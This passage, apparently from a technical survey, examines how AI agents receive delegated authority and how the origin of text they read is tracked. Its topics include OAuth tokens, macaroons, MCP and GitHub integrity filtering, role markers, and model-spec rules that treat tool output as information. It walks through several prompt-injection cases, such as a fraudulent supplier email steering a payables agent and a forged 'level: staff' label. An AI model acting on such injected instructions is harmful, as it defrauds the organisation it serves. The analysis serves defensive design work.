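The subject may also come from a program's own assertion. A program that starts a transaction itself, for instance on a timer, may have no incoming token to exchange. The draft lets such a program name a user in a token it signs itself, or even in an unsigned list of values, if the token service's policy permits. A later service that reads the records manager's name in `sub` can't tell from that claim whether the manager logged in or a program supplied the name.

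By August 2026 the OAuth working group had reached consensus on the draft and was preparing it for the IETF's final reviews.

### Adding agents to transaction tokens

*Transaction Tokens For Agents* (Raut, 2026) extends the design so that a company's internal services can detect that an agent is involved. The `act` claim identifies the agent, and the `sub` claim identifies the person it acts for. If the agent is working on its own initiative, `sub` identifies the agent itself.

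An optional claim, `agentic_ctx`, describes the agents in the chain in more detail. It can include a fingerprint of an agent's standing instructions, the agent's workload identity and evidence about the machine it runs on. The token service has to get this information from a registry or from attestation, because a compromised agent could lie about itself.

The service also calculates an assurance level for the whole chain, equal to the lowest level of any agent in it. If an outside company's assistant, rated "low", sends a request to an internal billing agent rated "high", the transaction stays "low". This prevents what Raut calls "identity laundering", in which an unverified agent gets past a check by sending its request through a trusted one.

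The idea is sound, but it rates programs and not the text they read. In the payables example, a request from the supplier's own agent would lower the rating because it adds an outside agent to the chain. An email from a stranger would leave the rating high because the only agent in the chain is the company's own, even though the company knows far less about the stranger.

The proposal also has little standing so far. Raut submitted it as an individual, and no IETF working group had adopted it when the second revision appeared in May 2026. That revision was due to expire on 23 November.

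### Tokens that holders can narrow

With token exchange, a program must go back to the authorisation server each time it gives another program a more limited token. *Capability tokens* let the holder create the more limited token without contacting the server. They apply Hardy's idea that permission to use something should come with the reference to it. The best-known kind is the *macaroon*, which Birgisson and colleagues introduced in 2014.

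A macaroon starts with a secret key K that only the issuing service has. Suppose the supplier database issues one to the payables agent, with the identifier "edit supplier records". The agent wants to give the banking tool a more limited version, so it adds two conditions, known as *caveats*. Each step uses the previous result as the key:

σ₀ = HMAC(K, "edit supplier records")

σ₁ = HMAC(σ₀, "supplier = 2207")

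σ₂ = HMAC(σ₁, "before 12:05")

The agent passes on the identifier, the two caveats and σ₂. The database repeats the calculation from K, compares the result with σ₂ and checks that the request meets both caveats. The banking tool could add a third caveat by computing HMAC(σ₂, new caveat). It would need σ₁ to remove the second caveat, and it cannot feasibly work out σ₁ from σ₂. Each holder can therefore narrow the rights it passes on but cannot widen them.

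Biscuit, a newer format, does the same with public-key signatures, so a service can check a token without holding a secret that would also let it create one.

This suits chains of agents better than basic token exchange, where the standard leaves it to local policy whether the server issues a narrower token. Someone still has to choose the caveats. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026), a survey of the field, describes a system called CAPMAS that selects a scope based on the task's meaning and then issues macaroons. The survey points out that the choice of scope may depend on a model, and that the cryptography only prevents later holders from expanding that scope. If a model that had read the fraudulent email chose the caveats, it might produce a token that allowed only one change, to account 4471.

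### Audience rules in the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) uses OAuth for servers reached over the web. Under its *Authorization* (2026), the agent's software is the client and the MCP server is the protected service. The Agentic AI Foundation compares the authorisation server to a passport office and the MCP server to a bouncer, who checks both that the passport is valid and that house rules allow the visitor in.

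When the client requests a token, it must include a `resource` value, the address of the MCP server it intends to call. The authorisation server can then restrict the token's audience to that server. The MCP server must reject any token not issued for it. If the agent connects to a weather service run by a criminal, the criminal receives a token that works only at that service. Without the restriction, the criminal might also have been able to use the token to access the supplier database.

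The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) also forbids a server from passing a client's token on to another service. In the payables example, the banking tool would have to obtain a separate token for the database. Forwarding the agent's token would be simpler, but the database would then have to accept tokens meant for other services, which would remove the protection against the criminal's weather service. The request would also reach the database under the agent's name, even though the banking tool had sent it and might have altered it. Kasselman and colleagues also discourage forwarding because it increases the risk that someone will steal the token and use it to move from one system to the next.

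MCP's rules address a narrower confused deputy problem than Hardy's. Some MCP servers connect to another company's service under a single fixed client name. Once a user has approved that name, the other company may skip its approval page, and an attacker who registers a new program with the MCP server can exploit the old approval. The server must therefore ask the user to approve each newly registered program, but this rule doesn't cover an email that misleads an approved agent.

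The rules also let an agent gain permissions during a task. When a token lacks a necessary scope, the server should report which scope is missing, and a client acting for a user should then request a new token. The request should include the old scopes as well as the missing one, so that the client doesn't lose permissions it needs elsewhere. An injected instruction can trigger such a request, and a records manager who is used to approving them may approve it.

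Authorisation is optional in MCP. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026) found that over 40% of 7,973 live servers exposed tools with no authentication. All 119 OAuth-enabled servers that the researchers tested had at least one flaw.

### A valid token for a change nobody requested

Even a perfect implementation would not stop the payables agent from acting on the fraudulent email. Suppose the records manager approves the agent's access on Monday so that it can keep supplier records up to date. The authorisation server also gives the harness a *refresh token*, which it can use to get new access tokens without asking for approval again. On Wednesday the helpdesk delivers the email, the model follows its instructions, and the harness calls the banking tool to enter account 4471.

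The banking tool exchanges its token and calls the database. The token has a valid signature, the right audience, and a scope that covers bank details, and it has not expired. Its subject is the records manager, who let the agent change supplier records. The database makes the change, although the records manager may not be at work.

Suppose the records manager had phoned the supplier on Wednesday and personally told the agent to enter account 4471. The harness would have sent the same request with an equivalent token, different only in its times and identifiers. Any rule based only on the request and the relevant content of the token would give the same answer in both cases. Without further information, the database must either accept the fraudulent change or refuse the honest one.

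According to Zhou and Zhang, a retrieved document can supply facts for a decision, and a trusted directory can supply evidence about the right recipient, but entering the agent's context doesn't give either one the authority to approve anything. The token in the example does not enforce this principle, because it doesn't show what was in the context.

One remedy is to ask for approval of the specific operation. *OAuth Transaction Authorization Challenge* (Rosomakho, 2026) proposes that a service answer a sensitive request with a challenge. The client takes the challenge to the authorisation server, which obtains any approval needed from a person or organisation. Zhou and Zhang describe SUDP, a system in which the user approves a standard description of an operation, and a separate program that holds the credentials carries out only the matching operation. Like a signed purchase mandate, this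 kind of approval would be tied to account 4471 rather than to supplier records in general.

Kasselman and colleagues require the user's confirmation to be tied to a grant from the authorisation server, for example through a notification on the user's phone, so a pop-up in the agent's own software is not enough. They admit that the existing protocol for such notifications is poorly suited to confirmations in the middle of a task.

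### Testing whether tokens confine a hijacked agent

If a company can't stop every injected instruction, it can at least limit what a hijacked agent is able to do. Dantuluri and Sundi (2026), in *Delegation Without Trust*, take this as their standard. They assume that an attacker fully controls the model's output and ask whether the agent can still exceed the authority that someone delegated to it. They consider four threats:

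| Threat | What it would mean for the payables agent |
|---|---|
| Confused deputy | An injected email leads the agent to use its own permissions for the attacker. |
| Token theft and replay | An attacker copies a token and uses it from another machine. |
| Privilege escalation | Injected text leads the agent to obtain a wider scope or call a tool outside its task. |
| Compromised sub-agent | An attacker controls a helper agent that has more permissions than its part of the work requires. |

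They then examined three popular kits for building agents, and MCP, in their default settings. The methods differed:

| Framework | Method | Protection by default |
|---|---|---|
| LangGraph | Ran a real workflow with a scripted agent instead of a model | None against any of the four threats |
| CrewAI | Inspected the code that runs tools | None |
| AutoGen | Inspected the code that runs tools | None |
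| MCP | Analysed the July 2026 authorisation rules | Partial against token theft, none against the others |

The result for the three kits is believable and not very surprising, since none of them is presented as an authorisation system. The findings for MCP are less reliable, because the paper's two summaries of it are inconsistent about whether it partly provides key rotation, revocation and audit.

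Dantuluri and Sundi also built a *broker*, a program of about 160 lines that stands between agents and tools. Each agent has a workload identity. When one agent delegates to another, the broker issues a new short-lived token that covers only the delegated task and works only for the receiving agent. The broker checks every tool call without using a model.

In the researchers' tests, all four attacks succeeded against a default system in which every agent held the same broad bearer token, and the broker blocked all four. The broker also resisted 11 attacks on its own design and accepted none of 200,000 forged tokens. As the researchers had expected, a stolen token worked when the attacker could also present the victim's workload identity. Each decision took about 2.6 microseconds, which is negligible compared with the time a model takes to answer.

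In 2,000 randomly generated cases of delegation, set in an artificial environment with 8,100 possible actions, a compromised sub-agent could carry out all 8,100 actions with the broad token and an average of 1.5 with the broker.

These scenarios are synthetic, and no live model took part. Both researchers work at VotalAI, which sells a product for controlling agents, and they have not released the broker's code. The size of the fall also follows largely from the set-up, because the researchers put 8,100 actions in the environment and the average delegated task included 1.5. They say the reduction matters less than the sub-agent's reach staying the same size as its task, however large the company's systems become.

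"Blocked" here also means only that the action fell outside the token's caveats. The broker doesn't stop harmful actions that fall within them. If the delegated task is to change suppliers' bank accounts, the broker would allow the fraudulent change to account 4471 and keep a complete audit record of it. The attack blocked in the confused deputy test must therefore have required something that the narrowed token didn't allow.

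Such a broker is still useful because, with one in place, a payables agent that reads a malicious email could damage supplier records but not the payroll or the customer database. The protection is weakest where the agent's ordinary work is dangerous.

### The case for authenticated delegation

*Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents* (South, Marro and colleagues, 2025) proposes a signed credential that builds on OAuth and contains the agent's identity, its permissions and information about the user. The credential is meant to let any service an agent calls verify that the caller is an AI agent, that it acts for a particular person, and that this person has given it the permissions it needs.

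They argue that the alternatives are one-sided. A user can prompt an agent to stay within a budget when it books a flight, but the airline doesn't know about the budget and the agent may ignore it. Under their scheme, the booking service would store the card details and enforce the spending limit. The scheme would also let a person give an assistant separate credentials for work and private life, so that a service could refuse to let it fill in a personal form using work documents.

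The credential could also list what an agent can't do. In one example, a doctor's agent logs in to a telemedicine site with ordinary credentials and receives a patient's full record, including a specialist's video that it can't process. The agent makes a recommendation from the text alone, and the doctor overlooks the standard warning about missing information. If the credentials had listed this limitation, the site could have asked a person to watch the video.

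South and colleagues support these claims with examples rather than experiments, but the argument for accountability is strong. Accountability is also the part of the problem that tokens handle well, because a service that knows whose agent it is dealing with can apply that person's limits and contact them when something goes wrong.

The argument is weaker when it comes to identifying the source of an instruction. In another of their examples, a hospital's agent sends treatment claims to an insurer's agent, and authentication prevents a stranger from posing as the hospital. But the hospital's real agent may have read a patient's letter containing an injected instruction to add a treatment that never took place. The false claim would arrive with the hospital's valid credential. The insurer could use that credential to identify the hospital and seek repayment, but not to trace the instruction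 to the letter.

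## How can the relaying service tell the agent who wrote each item?

The operator of a relaying service often has a record of who wrote each item, even though the connection to the agent doesn't show the agent who that was. GitHub's records show which account posted an issue and whether that account belongs to a project maintainer. A helpdesk's records show whether an employee typed a passage after logging in or it came in by email.

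The operator can use these records to filter out text from strangers before it reaches the agent. Alternatively, the relay can attach an *integrity label* to each item, which indicates how far its source is trusted to influence actions, and let the receiving side decide how to handle the item. GitHub has built a filter, and engineers at GitHub and OpenAI have proposed labels for the Model Context Protocol (MCP).

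### Five levels of trust on GitHub

GitHub Agentic Workflows lets a project's maintainers describe a recurring job in ordinary language, such as sorting new issues, and have an AI agent do it. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, from the company's research group, explains how these workflows decide what the agent may read. The filter gives every issue, comment and pull request (a proposed change to a project's files) one of five levels. GitHub's reference documentation defines them as follows:

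| Level | What qualifies |
|---|---|
| `merged` | Pull requests that have become part of the project, and any change on its main branch, whoever wrote it |
| `approved` | Items by the owner, members and invited collaborators; pull requests that don't come from an outside copy of the project; recognised bots; everything in a private repository |
| `unapproved` | Items by contributors, including first-time contributors |
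| `none` | Items by everyone else |
| `blocked` | Items by accounts on the workflow's block list |

The maintainers choose the lowest level that the agent may see:

```
tools:
  github:
    allowed-repos: ["myorg/web-app"]
    min-integrity: approved
```

A gateway between the agent and GitHub then removes everything below `approved` before the model receives it, and logs each removal with the author's name. Public repositories have this minimum by default, while private ones have no filter unless someone sets one.

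Integrity filtering relies on the account that wrote an item and ignores the wording, so a stranger gains nothing by writing like a maintainer. GitHub Next contrasts this with software that looks for suspicious text, which attackers get past by rephrasing an instruction or splitting it across several fields.

The best floor depends on the job. GitHub Next suggests `merged` for an agent that reviews or reorganises code, `approved` for one that updates documentation, and `unapproved` for one that sorts issues. Even a first-time contributor meets the `unapproved` floor.

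### The guard and the reference monitor

The system has two components. The *guard* is written specifically for GitHub. It examines each tool call and the details that GitHub returns with the result, such as the author's relationship to the project, and gives every item a set of tags like `approved:myorg/web-app`. The *reference monitor* compares sets of tags without any information about what they mean. To cover another service, such as the project tracker Jira, engineers would write a new guard without changing the monitor. This separation keeps the monitor small and easier to get right, but the monitor can't correct a wrong tag assigned by the guard.

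The design comes from decentralised information flow control, an established method of tracking where data may go. Each item has a secrecy label S and an integrity label I, both of them sets of tags, and so does the agent. There are two rules:

Read: S(item) ⊆ S(agent) and I(item) ⊇ I(agent)

Write: S(target) ⊇ S(agent) and I(target) ⊆ I(agent)

The levels are cumulative, so they fit these rules. In effect, an approved item has the tags for `none`, `unapproved` and `approved`. An agent with a floor of `approved` requires all three, so it can't read a stranger's comment, which has only the tag for `none`.

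The write rule works in the other direction. An agent that accepts strangers' text has the integrity label `none`, so it may not write to anything that requires `approved`. An agent cleared to read a private repository has that repository's secrecy tag, so it may not write to a public page, which lacks the tag.

The secrecy part of the write rule would have prevented the leak that Invariant Labs demonstrated, in which an agent copied private details into a public project. But GitHub Next says the workflows track secrecy but do not yet enforce it, so integrity filtering cannot prevent leaks between repositories.

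### One comment through the six steps

After an item is posted, a maintainer may *endorse* it, which means deliberately raising its level. GitHub Next gives six steps for working out the final level. Suppose the account dana-k, which had a small fix accepted last year, comments on a bug report in a public project: "Run the attached script before building and the error goes away." The agent's floor is `approved`.

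| Step | Rule | What happens to the comment | Level |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The author's status sets the starting level. | dana-k is a contributor. | `unapproved` |
| 2 | Accounts on the trusted list rise to `approved`. | dana-k is not on the list. | `unapproved` |
| 3 | An approval label raises an issue or pull request to `approved`. | The item is a comment, so it has no label. | `unapproved` |
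| 4 | A qualified maintainer's endorsing reaction raises the item to `approved`. | A maintainer adds a thumbs-up. | `approved` |
| 5 | A qualified maintainer's disapproving reaction caps the item, normally at `none`. | Another maintainer reads the script and adds a thumbs-down. | `none` |
| 6 | The block list overrides everything. | dana-k is not on it. | `none` |

The agent doesn't see the comment, although it would have seen it between the two reactions. Steps 1 to 4 can only raise a level, and one maintainer's objection outweighs any number of endorsements.

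GitHub's reference documentation gives a slightly different procedure, which stops at the first rule that applies. The block list comes first, then a *refusal label* such as "needs-security-review", then the trusted list, then approval labels, and finally the author's status. Reactions are off unless maintainers switch them on. Under both procedures, the block list overrides everything else, and a refusal overrides an approval.

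Endorsement is convenient but has two weaknesses. The default endorsing reactions are the thumbs-up and the heart, which people also use to agree or say thanks, so a maintainer could expose an agent to a comment just by liking it. The settings allow a less common reaction, which would be safer. An author can also edit a comment after a maintainer has endorsed it. GitHub doesn't mention a check for this in its description of the filter, and without one, the endorsement could cover words the maintainer never saw.

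Approval labels have a similar problem. GitHub Next's sample settings use "triaged" as an approval label, and the reference documentation describes a check for the label itself, not for who added it. If a triage agent can add the label, a stranger could write an issue that persuades the agent to do so. A second agent that requires a higher level of trust would then read the issue as approved. Maintainers should therefore choose a label that no agent can apply.

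An approved comment also isn't necessarily an order. The level shows that someone with a recognised role wrote or endorsed the text, but a collaborator who may fix spelling mistakes has the same level as the owner. If the agent can also publish releases, the project needs a separate rule about who may request a release.

### Lockdown mode and its flaw

GitHub's MCP server has an older and simpler filter called lockdown mode. In public repositories, it shows the agent only items from people with push access (permission to change the project's files). GitHub recommends switching it off for jobs such as triage and spam detection, where the agent has to read everyone's text.

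To apply the filter, the server has to look up each author's access. GitLab's *Advisories for Golang/Github.com/Github/Github-Mcp-Server package* (2026) describes a flaw in these lookups when several people shared one server over HTTP. The server created a single store for the lookups with the credentials of the first person to log in, and kept using those credentials to check authors for everyone else. Two users may have access to different repositories, so a lookup could return a result that was correct for the first person but wrong for the current user. The flaw recreated Hardy's confused deputy problem in a filter meant to guard against it.

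The newer filter also has a gap. Some workflows run set-up steps before the agent starts, and a separate proxy filters what those steps fetch from GitHub. According to the reference documentation, this proxy applies the floor but not the block list, the trusted list or the labels. Suppose an intruder takes over a collaborator's account and the maintainers add the account to the block list. The account still has collaborator status, so a set-up step can fetch its comments. If that step saves them in a file that the agent later reads, the agent will see them despite the block.

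### Trust labels for the Model Context Protocol

GitHub's guard works only with GitHub. An agent that also reads tickets, chat messages and web pages would need a common way to receive labels from each service.

MCP has had *annotations* since March 2025, but they describe tools. They indicate whether a tool only reads, whether it may destroy data, whether it is safe to call repeatedly and whether it deals with the outside world. A tool that fetches email has the same annotations whether the chief executive or a fraudster wrote the message.

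Specification Enhancement Proposal 1913 (SEP-1913), Trust and Sensitivity Annotations, would add labels to the results that tools return. Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI are its authors. Morrow's summary appears in the discussion of a related proposal, *SEP-1862* (SamMorrowDrums, 2025), and lists five fields:

| Field | What a server could report about a result |
|---|---|
| `sensitiveHint` | How sensitive the data is |
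| `privateHint` | Whether the data is private |
| `openWorldHint` | Whether it involves outside sources |
| `maliciousActivityHint` | Whether there are signs of an attack |
| `attribution` | Where the data came from |

In *MCP annotations are a UX layer, not a security layer*, gyorgy writes that sensitivity can be low, medium or high. A server could label each item separately, which matters when a search returns a colleague's message beside a stranger's. The agent's software would also attach labels to its requests, so the next server could take them into account.

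The labels build up as the agent works. Dumbris (2026), in *MCP Tool Annotations*, summarises the rules, which amount to the following:

sensitivity = max(old, new)

each yes/no hint = old OR new

attribution = old ∪ new

Suppose the payables agent reads the ticket about account 4471, then the supplier's record, then a public page of bank codes:

| After reading | Sensitivity | Private | Outside sources | Attribution |
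|---|---|---|---|---|
| The ticket | Low | No | Yes | Email |
| The supplier's record | High | Yes | Yes | Email, supplier database |
| The bank codes | High | Yes | Yes | Email, supplier database, web page |

Reading the harmless web page doesn't lower the sensitivity again. The agent's software could now refuse to send anything outside the company, because the session contains both private data and text from strangers. That would be a good defence against leaks, but it wouldn't stop the fraudulent change of bank account, which happens inside the company's own database. The labels also describe the whole session, so they can't show whether the email or something else led to a particular request.

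MCP's July revision removed sessions (Model Context Protocol, 2026), so each request now stands alone and the protocol has nowhere to keep these running totals. The agent's software, or a gateway in front of the servers, would have to store the labels and decide when to reset them. Without resets, an agent that ran all day would soon have the most restrictive labels available.

SEP-1913 is still a draft and isn't in the Model Context Protocol's index of accepted and final proposals, which has entries up to October. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter*, from April 2026, leaves open whether tool responses should have annotations at all. The protocol's July revision added no trust labels, and they are not among the priorities in the roadmap that the Model Context Protocol (2026) updated in November. The next release is due on 30 March 2027, and an older proposal like this one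 needs a sponsoring group before its next formal review. In *added initial scaffolding files with python ref SDK*, kapil8811 has submitted an experimental Python kit that attaches the labels, combines them and applies policies to them.

### When the server itself is dishonest

A server writes its own annotations, and the protocol doesn't check them. During the original review, MCP co-creator Justin Spahr-Summers asked how a client could use a flag it couldn't trust. The specification calls every annotation a hint and tells clients not to rely on hints from untrusted servers. According to gyorgy, SEP-1913 has the same limit because it lets honest servers express more but doesn't help expose dishonest ones.

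The Model Context Protocol's maintainers agree that "An untrusted server can lie". They suggest asking whether any new annotation is a hint or a contract. If its value depends on its being true, they think it belongs in the authorisation layer, the transport or the runtime. A label that identifies an author looks much more like a contract than a hint.

The objection is sound, but it applies less to relays than to malicious servers, which could invent the text as well as falsify its author. In the GitHub and EchoLeak attacks, an outsider wrote the malicious text and the service only relayed it. GitHub had no reason to disguise who posted an issue, and an accurate label from it would have been useful.

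But a false label can still do extra damage by giving invented text an authority it would otherwise lack. For example, a weather service run by a criminal could label a forecast as an order from the company's records manager. The agent's software could guard against this by accepting a server's labels only for that server's own users. SPIFFE federation restricts outside organisations' keys in a similar way.

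One of several proposed ways to decide which servers to believe is a *registry*, a list of servers that someone has vetted. Stacklok's *Tool annotations are becoming the risk vocabulary for agentic systems*, a vendor's argument for this kind of governance, says that trustworthy annotations let a company set policy for a whole session without assuming the worst about every tool. A registry's reviewers can check a tool's fixed description fairly easily. Labels on results are harder to check because the server produces a new one for each email or issue, so the reviewers would have to examine the code that assigns the labels, and do so again after every update.

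### Admitting servers with a signed document

Metere (2026), in *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, proposes that a server publish a short signed document stating how sensitive the data it handles may be. Before using the server, the agent's software checks that:

- the document describes an MCP server and has a signature;
- the signing key is on the company's own list and has not expired;
- the company allows that key to vouch for the stated level;
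- the signature is valid;
- the level is high enough for the task;
- the document covers the address of the server, if it lists any addresses.

The company also keeps a list of permitted tools for each server it admits, and the software blocks calls to any other tool before they reach the network. For instance, a company could let an agent search Gmail and write drafts, but not delete messages.

The check refused all 31 disguised tool names and 12 invalid documents in Metere's prepared tests. It also refused another 27,025 tool names and 14,378 forged documents produced by a small language model. These totals are weaker evidence than their size suggests, because the software accepts only exact names and the model had no signing key. The hand-written tests were probably more useful. They exposed a weakness in an earlier version, which did not tie a document to its server's address.

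Enclawed, Metere's company, has put the system into its products. Google doesn't publish a document for the Gmail connection that motivated the work, so Enclawed uses its own signed connector instead. The evidence in that case is Enclawed's decision to trust Google's server.

Metere says the system doesn't screen the content that crosses an admitted connection. If the company admits its helpdesk's server, a fraudster's email will arrive through it like any other ticket. Admission gives the company a reason to believe the helpdesk's labels, but the helpdesk still has to supply them.

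### Labelling at a gateway

The company can also assign labels itself. *Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026), a master's thesis at Brown University, describes SAMOS, in which a tool's developer or the company's administrator labels each tool. The labels mark what the tool reads and where it writes as high or low confidentiality. Every call passes through a gateway, which records what the session has accessed so far.

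Ntousakis works through the GitHub attack. Once the agent has read the public issues, the gateway labels the session "low". It then refuses the agent's request for a file from a private repository, which is labeled "high", so the private details never reach the model.

The gateway has to distinguish private repositories from public ones, but one tool reads both. Ntousakis suggests either having the tool report each repository's confidentiality or splitting it into two tools. Relying on the tool's report would again require trusting the server, and Ntousakis assumes that tools behave honestly. Splitting the tool lets the administrator fix the labels in advance, but gives the model more tools to choose from.

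SAMOS also labels confidentiality rather than authorship. A maintainer's public issue and a stranger's have the same effect on the session, so an agent could not use either one as a reason to consult private notes. The labels are manual and coarse, and the evidence is one worked example, with no measurement of how often the rules would interrupt ordinary work. GitHub's filter also enforces its rules at a gateway, but its guard uses GitHub's account records, so it can tell the maintainer from the stranger.

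### Where account labels mislead

An account's status is still only evidence of who wrote something. If an intruder takes over a maintainer's account, GitHub's filter will rate the intruder's comments as `approved`. GitHub Next acknowledges this and relies on other restrictions to reduce the damage, including a network firewall and limits on what the agent may publish. Maintainers can add the account to the block list once they notice the takeover.

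A second problem can occur even without an intruder. The label correctly identifies the account that posted an item, but that account may be relaying someone else's words. Suppose a maintainer receives a bug report by email and pastes it into a new issue for the team to discuss. The issue is labeled `approved` because a maintainer posted it, although a stranger wrote the text. Trusted bots can cause the same error. Dependabot, which GitHub's filter trusts by default, proposes updates to the outside software that a project uses, and its pull requests often include release notes written by that software's developers.

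Private repositories make this mistake more likely. GitHub's filter treats everything in them as `approved`, on the reasoning that only people with access can post there. But many companies connect other services to their private repositories. If one of these services automatically turns a customer's complaint or a crash report into an issue, an outsider's text gets the same `approved` level as an engineer's.

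Some jobs can't use a strict filter. GitHub's *[integrity] DIFC Integrity-Filtered Events Report* (2026), which covers the company's own workflows, recorded 174 removals on 31 March and 265 on 1 April. Two triage workflows accounted for 72% of them. Their agents repeatedly tried and failed to read issues from the community, then tried the same ones again on the next run. Security software could count these attempts as blocked threats, even though the agents were only trying to triage issues.

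Maintainers can lower the floor for such work. GitHub's *Example* of automated repository maintenance lowers it to `unapproved` so that the agent can see outside contributors' issues. A spam detector needs `none` because it has to read spam. At that level the filter removes only content from blocked accounts, so a stranger's injected instruction will get through. The project then has to rely on limiting what the agent can do.

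The GitLost attack shows what can happen when those limits are too loose. According to Aident's *How to Secure GitHub Agentic Workflows Against Prompt Injection*, Noma Security disclosed in July 2026 that an attacker could use a public issue to steer an Agentic Workflow that could access other repositories, including private ones, and post public comments. Aident, a vendor, recommends confining the agent to the current repository, cutting off its network access and allowing it one comment per run. These measures would reduce the harm even if the agent had to read every stranger's issue.

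### Labels for the helpdesk ticket

The company could write a guard for its helpdesk. It would label each part of a ticket separately, because one ticket can contain the words of several people:

| Part of the ticket | What the helpdesk can record | Level |
|---|---|---|
| Ticket number and arrival time | Its own software produced them | `system` |
| A support employee's note | Which employee was logged in | `staff` |
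| The supplier's email | The sending domain, the DKIM result and whether the domain matches the one on file | `outside` |
| A message quoted in that email | Nothing about who first wrote it | `outside` |

If the helpdesk delivers tickets through MCP, it doesn't have to wait for SEP-1913. Results already have a `_meta` field for extra information, and the company can define its own entry:

```
"content": [
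  {"type": "text", "text": "Our bank account is now 4471."}
],
"_meta": {
  "com.example/origin": [
    {"part": 0, "level": "outside", "channel": "email",
     "domain": "supplier.example", "dkim": "pass"}
  ]
}
```

MCP's maintainers recommend this field when the same organisation runs both ends, because other organisations' software won't recognise the entry. The helpdesk has to keep the label out of the text, because a fraudster could type "level: staff" at the top of an email. It should also sign the body so that no gateway can change the label unnoticed.

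If the company then relied on filtering alone, a floor of `staff` would hide every supplier's request from the payables agent. Lowering the floor to `outside` would let the agent see fraudulent requests along with honest ones, including any from an intruder in the bookkeeper's mailbox.

A better arrangement uses the write rule. Suppose the agent reads outside email, so it has only the `outside` tag. It may add an entry to a list of proposed changes, which accepts that tag, but it may not write to the bank details, which require a `records` tag. The records manager phones the supplier and approves the new number. A separate program that never reads the email then makes the change.

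The manager's approval should cover only the supplier and the account number. If it raised the whole ticket to `records`, any instruction hidden in the email would be raised too. The helpdesk should also let support employees quote a customer's words in a note with the original `outside` label attached. Otherwise, a fraudster's request copied into a note will reach the agent as the words of the company's own staff.

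## Does information about origin survive inside the agent, and does the model act on it?

Suppose the helpdesk signs every ticket and labels the supplier's email as `outside`, and the payables agent's harness checks the signature and reads the label. The harness then has good evidence about where the text came from, but the language model can use that evidence only if the harness includes it in the model's input.

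### Role markers

Before each call, the harness sends the model's input to the provider's interface as a list of items, each with a type. The provider's software joins the items into one sequence and puts a *role marker*, usually a reserved token, at the start of each item.

The main interfaces name and arrange these types differently. He, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *When Context Gets Root*, sort them into three levels:

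| Interface | System level | User level | Tool level |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI Chat Completions | System and developer messages | User messages | Tool messages |
| OpenAI Responses | System and developer messages | User messages | Function-output items |
| Anthropic Messages | System instructions | Ordinary content in user messages | Marked blocks inside user messages |
| Google Gemini Interactions | System instruction | User input | Function-result items |

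Anthropic's interface puts tool results inside user messages. Each block's type distinguishes tool results from the user's words, but a program that checked only the outer message would treat tool results as the user's words. For example, a tool that searched old logs for the user's requests could attribute the supplier's email to the records manager.

Three levels also leave out most of what the harness knows:

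| Item | What the harness knows | Marker |
|---|---|---|
| Standing instructions | They come from the company's own configuration. | System |
| A request to clear today's tickets | The records manager logged in and sent it. | User |
| The supplier's email | The helpdesk signed the ticket and labelled this part `outside`. | Tool |
| The supplier's existing record | It came from the company's database over mutual TLS. | Tool |

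The email and the record get the same marker, although the company has far better reason to believe the record. The harness can label the email as written by an outsider, but the model receives that label as text too, and a fraudster can imitate it.

The marker is only an assertion by the harness. It has no signature or certificate, and the model checks nothing when it reads "user". The model provider can't check it either, because its interface accepts a user message from any program with a valid API key. In the notation of Lampson and colleagues, everything the model reads has the form "harness says (manager says r)", and the model has to assume that the harness correctly reports who said what. That is usually a fair assumption about the company's own software, but the model can't detect when the assumption is wrong.

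Information about origin can be lost as soon as the text arrives. If a new ticket starts the payables agent when no person is present, the harness must still put something in the user message. The easiest choice is the ticket, which would give the supplier's email the same marker as an order from the records manager. Cline's issue bot had much the same problem with issue titles.

### Training models to rank sources

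A role marker has an effect only if the model takes it into account. In *The Instruction Hierarchy* (2024), Wallace, Xiao and colleagues at OpenAI argued that models were vulnerable because they often gave an operator's instructions the same priority as text from strangers. They proposed ranking system messages first, then user messages, then the model's own outputs, and tool results last.

"The Instruction Hierarchy" used two kinds of example to train GPT-3.5 to prioritize higher-level instructions. In the first kind, the instructions were compatible. A request such as "write a 20-line poem in Spanish" was split into parts placed at different levels, and the model was trained to answer the whole request. In the second kind, a lower-level instruction conflicted with a higher one, and the model was trained to answer as if it had never seen the lower one. After this training, GPT-3.5 was much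 more resistant to attacks, including some kinds that the training had left out, but it also refused some harmless requests that resembled attacks.

He and colleagues argue that models also learn the ranking from ordinary training data. Most records of chatbot conversations contain system instructions that the model obeyed, so a model trained on these records will tend to obey system instructions too. This explanation is plausible, but they don't test it.

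In both cases the model has learned a tendency to follow the ranking. The software around the model doesn't prevent a tool result from influencing the next action, and Ye and colleagues found that a passage's style can influence the model more than its marker does.

### The rules at OpenAI and Anthropic

OpenAI's first Model Spec, from May 2024, gave the highest priority to instructions from the platform, followed by those from the developer, the user and tools. In *On OpenAI's Model Spec*, the commentator Mowshowitz quotes its rule for quoted text, file attachments and tool outputs. By default, the model should assume that they contain untrusted data, and it must treat any instructions in them as information rather than commands. Because this is a default, a user can still authorize the model to follow a recipe or a checklist.

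OpenAI published a new version on 29 October 2026. OpenAI's *An updated Model Spec for more capable and beneficial AI* explains that models need judgement for situations that their instructions don't address. Mowshowitz (2026), in *OpenAI Updates Its Model Spec*, compared the two most recent versions and found the ranking "fundamentally unchanged". Three additions matter for relayed messages:

- Manipulation by third parties is now a listed source of risk, separate from harmful instructions by users and developers.
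- The model should not get around a restriction by delegating the forbidden action or doing it indirectly.
- A new subsection covers how conversations, memories and other context should inform the model's view of what people want, as Newsroom America's *OpenAI Updates Model Spec Around Five Core Values* (2026) reports.

Memory makes origin more important. A memory can be good evidence of the user's wishes only if the user's own words led to it. If the agent saved it after reading a stranger's email, it is evidence of what the stranger wanted.

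The constitution Anthropic published for Claude in January 2026 also treats instructions in documents, search results and tool outputs as information, not as orders. Its ranking of Anthropic, operators and users is explicitly not strict, because users keep some protections that operators can't remove. Claude should be suspicious of unverified claims that a message comes from Anthropic, and should scrutinise requests to unlock behaviour more than requests for caution. This difference is sensible, since a false request for caution usually does less harm.

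The constitution allows another AI agent to be Claude's operator or user, so being an AI doesn't settle whether an agent may give instructions. When an agent that lacks the authority to approve something passes on an approval, Claude should treat the message as a report that someone approved. This is the quoting rule from the logic of authentication.

Such rules help when a report is recognizable to the model as a report, but not when the harness has already presented it as the approver's own message.

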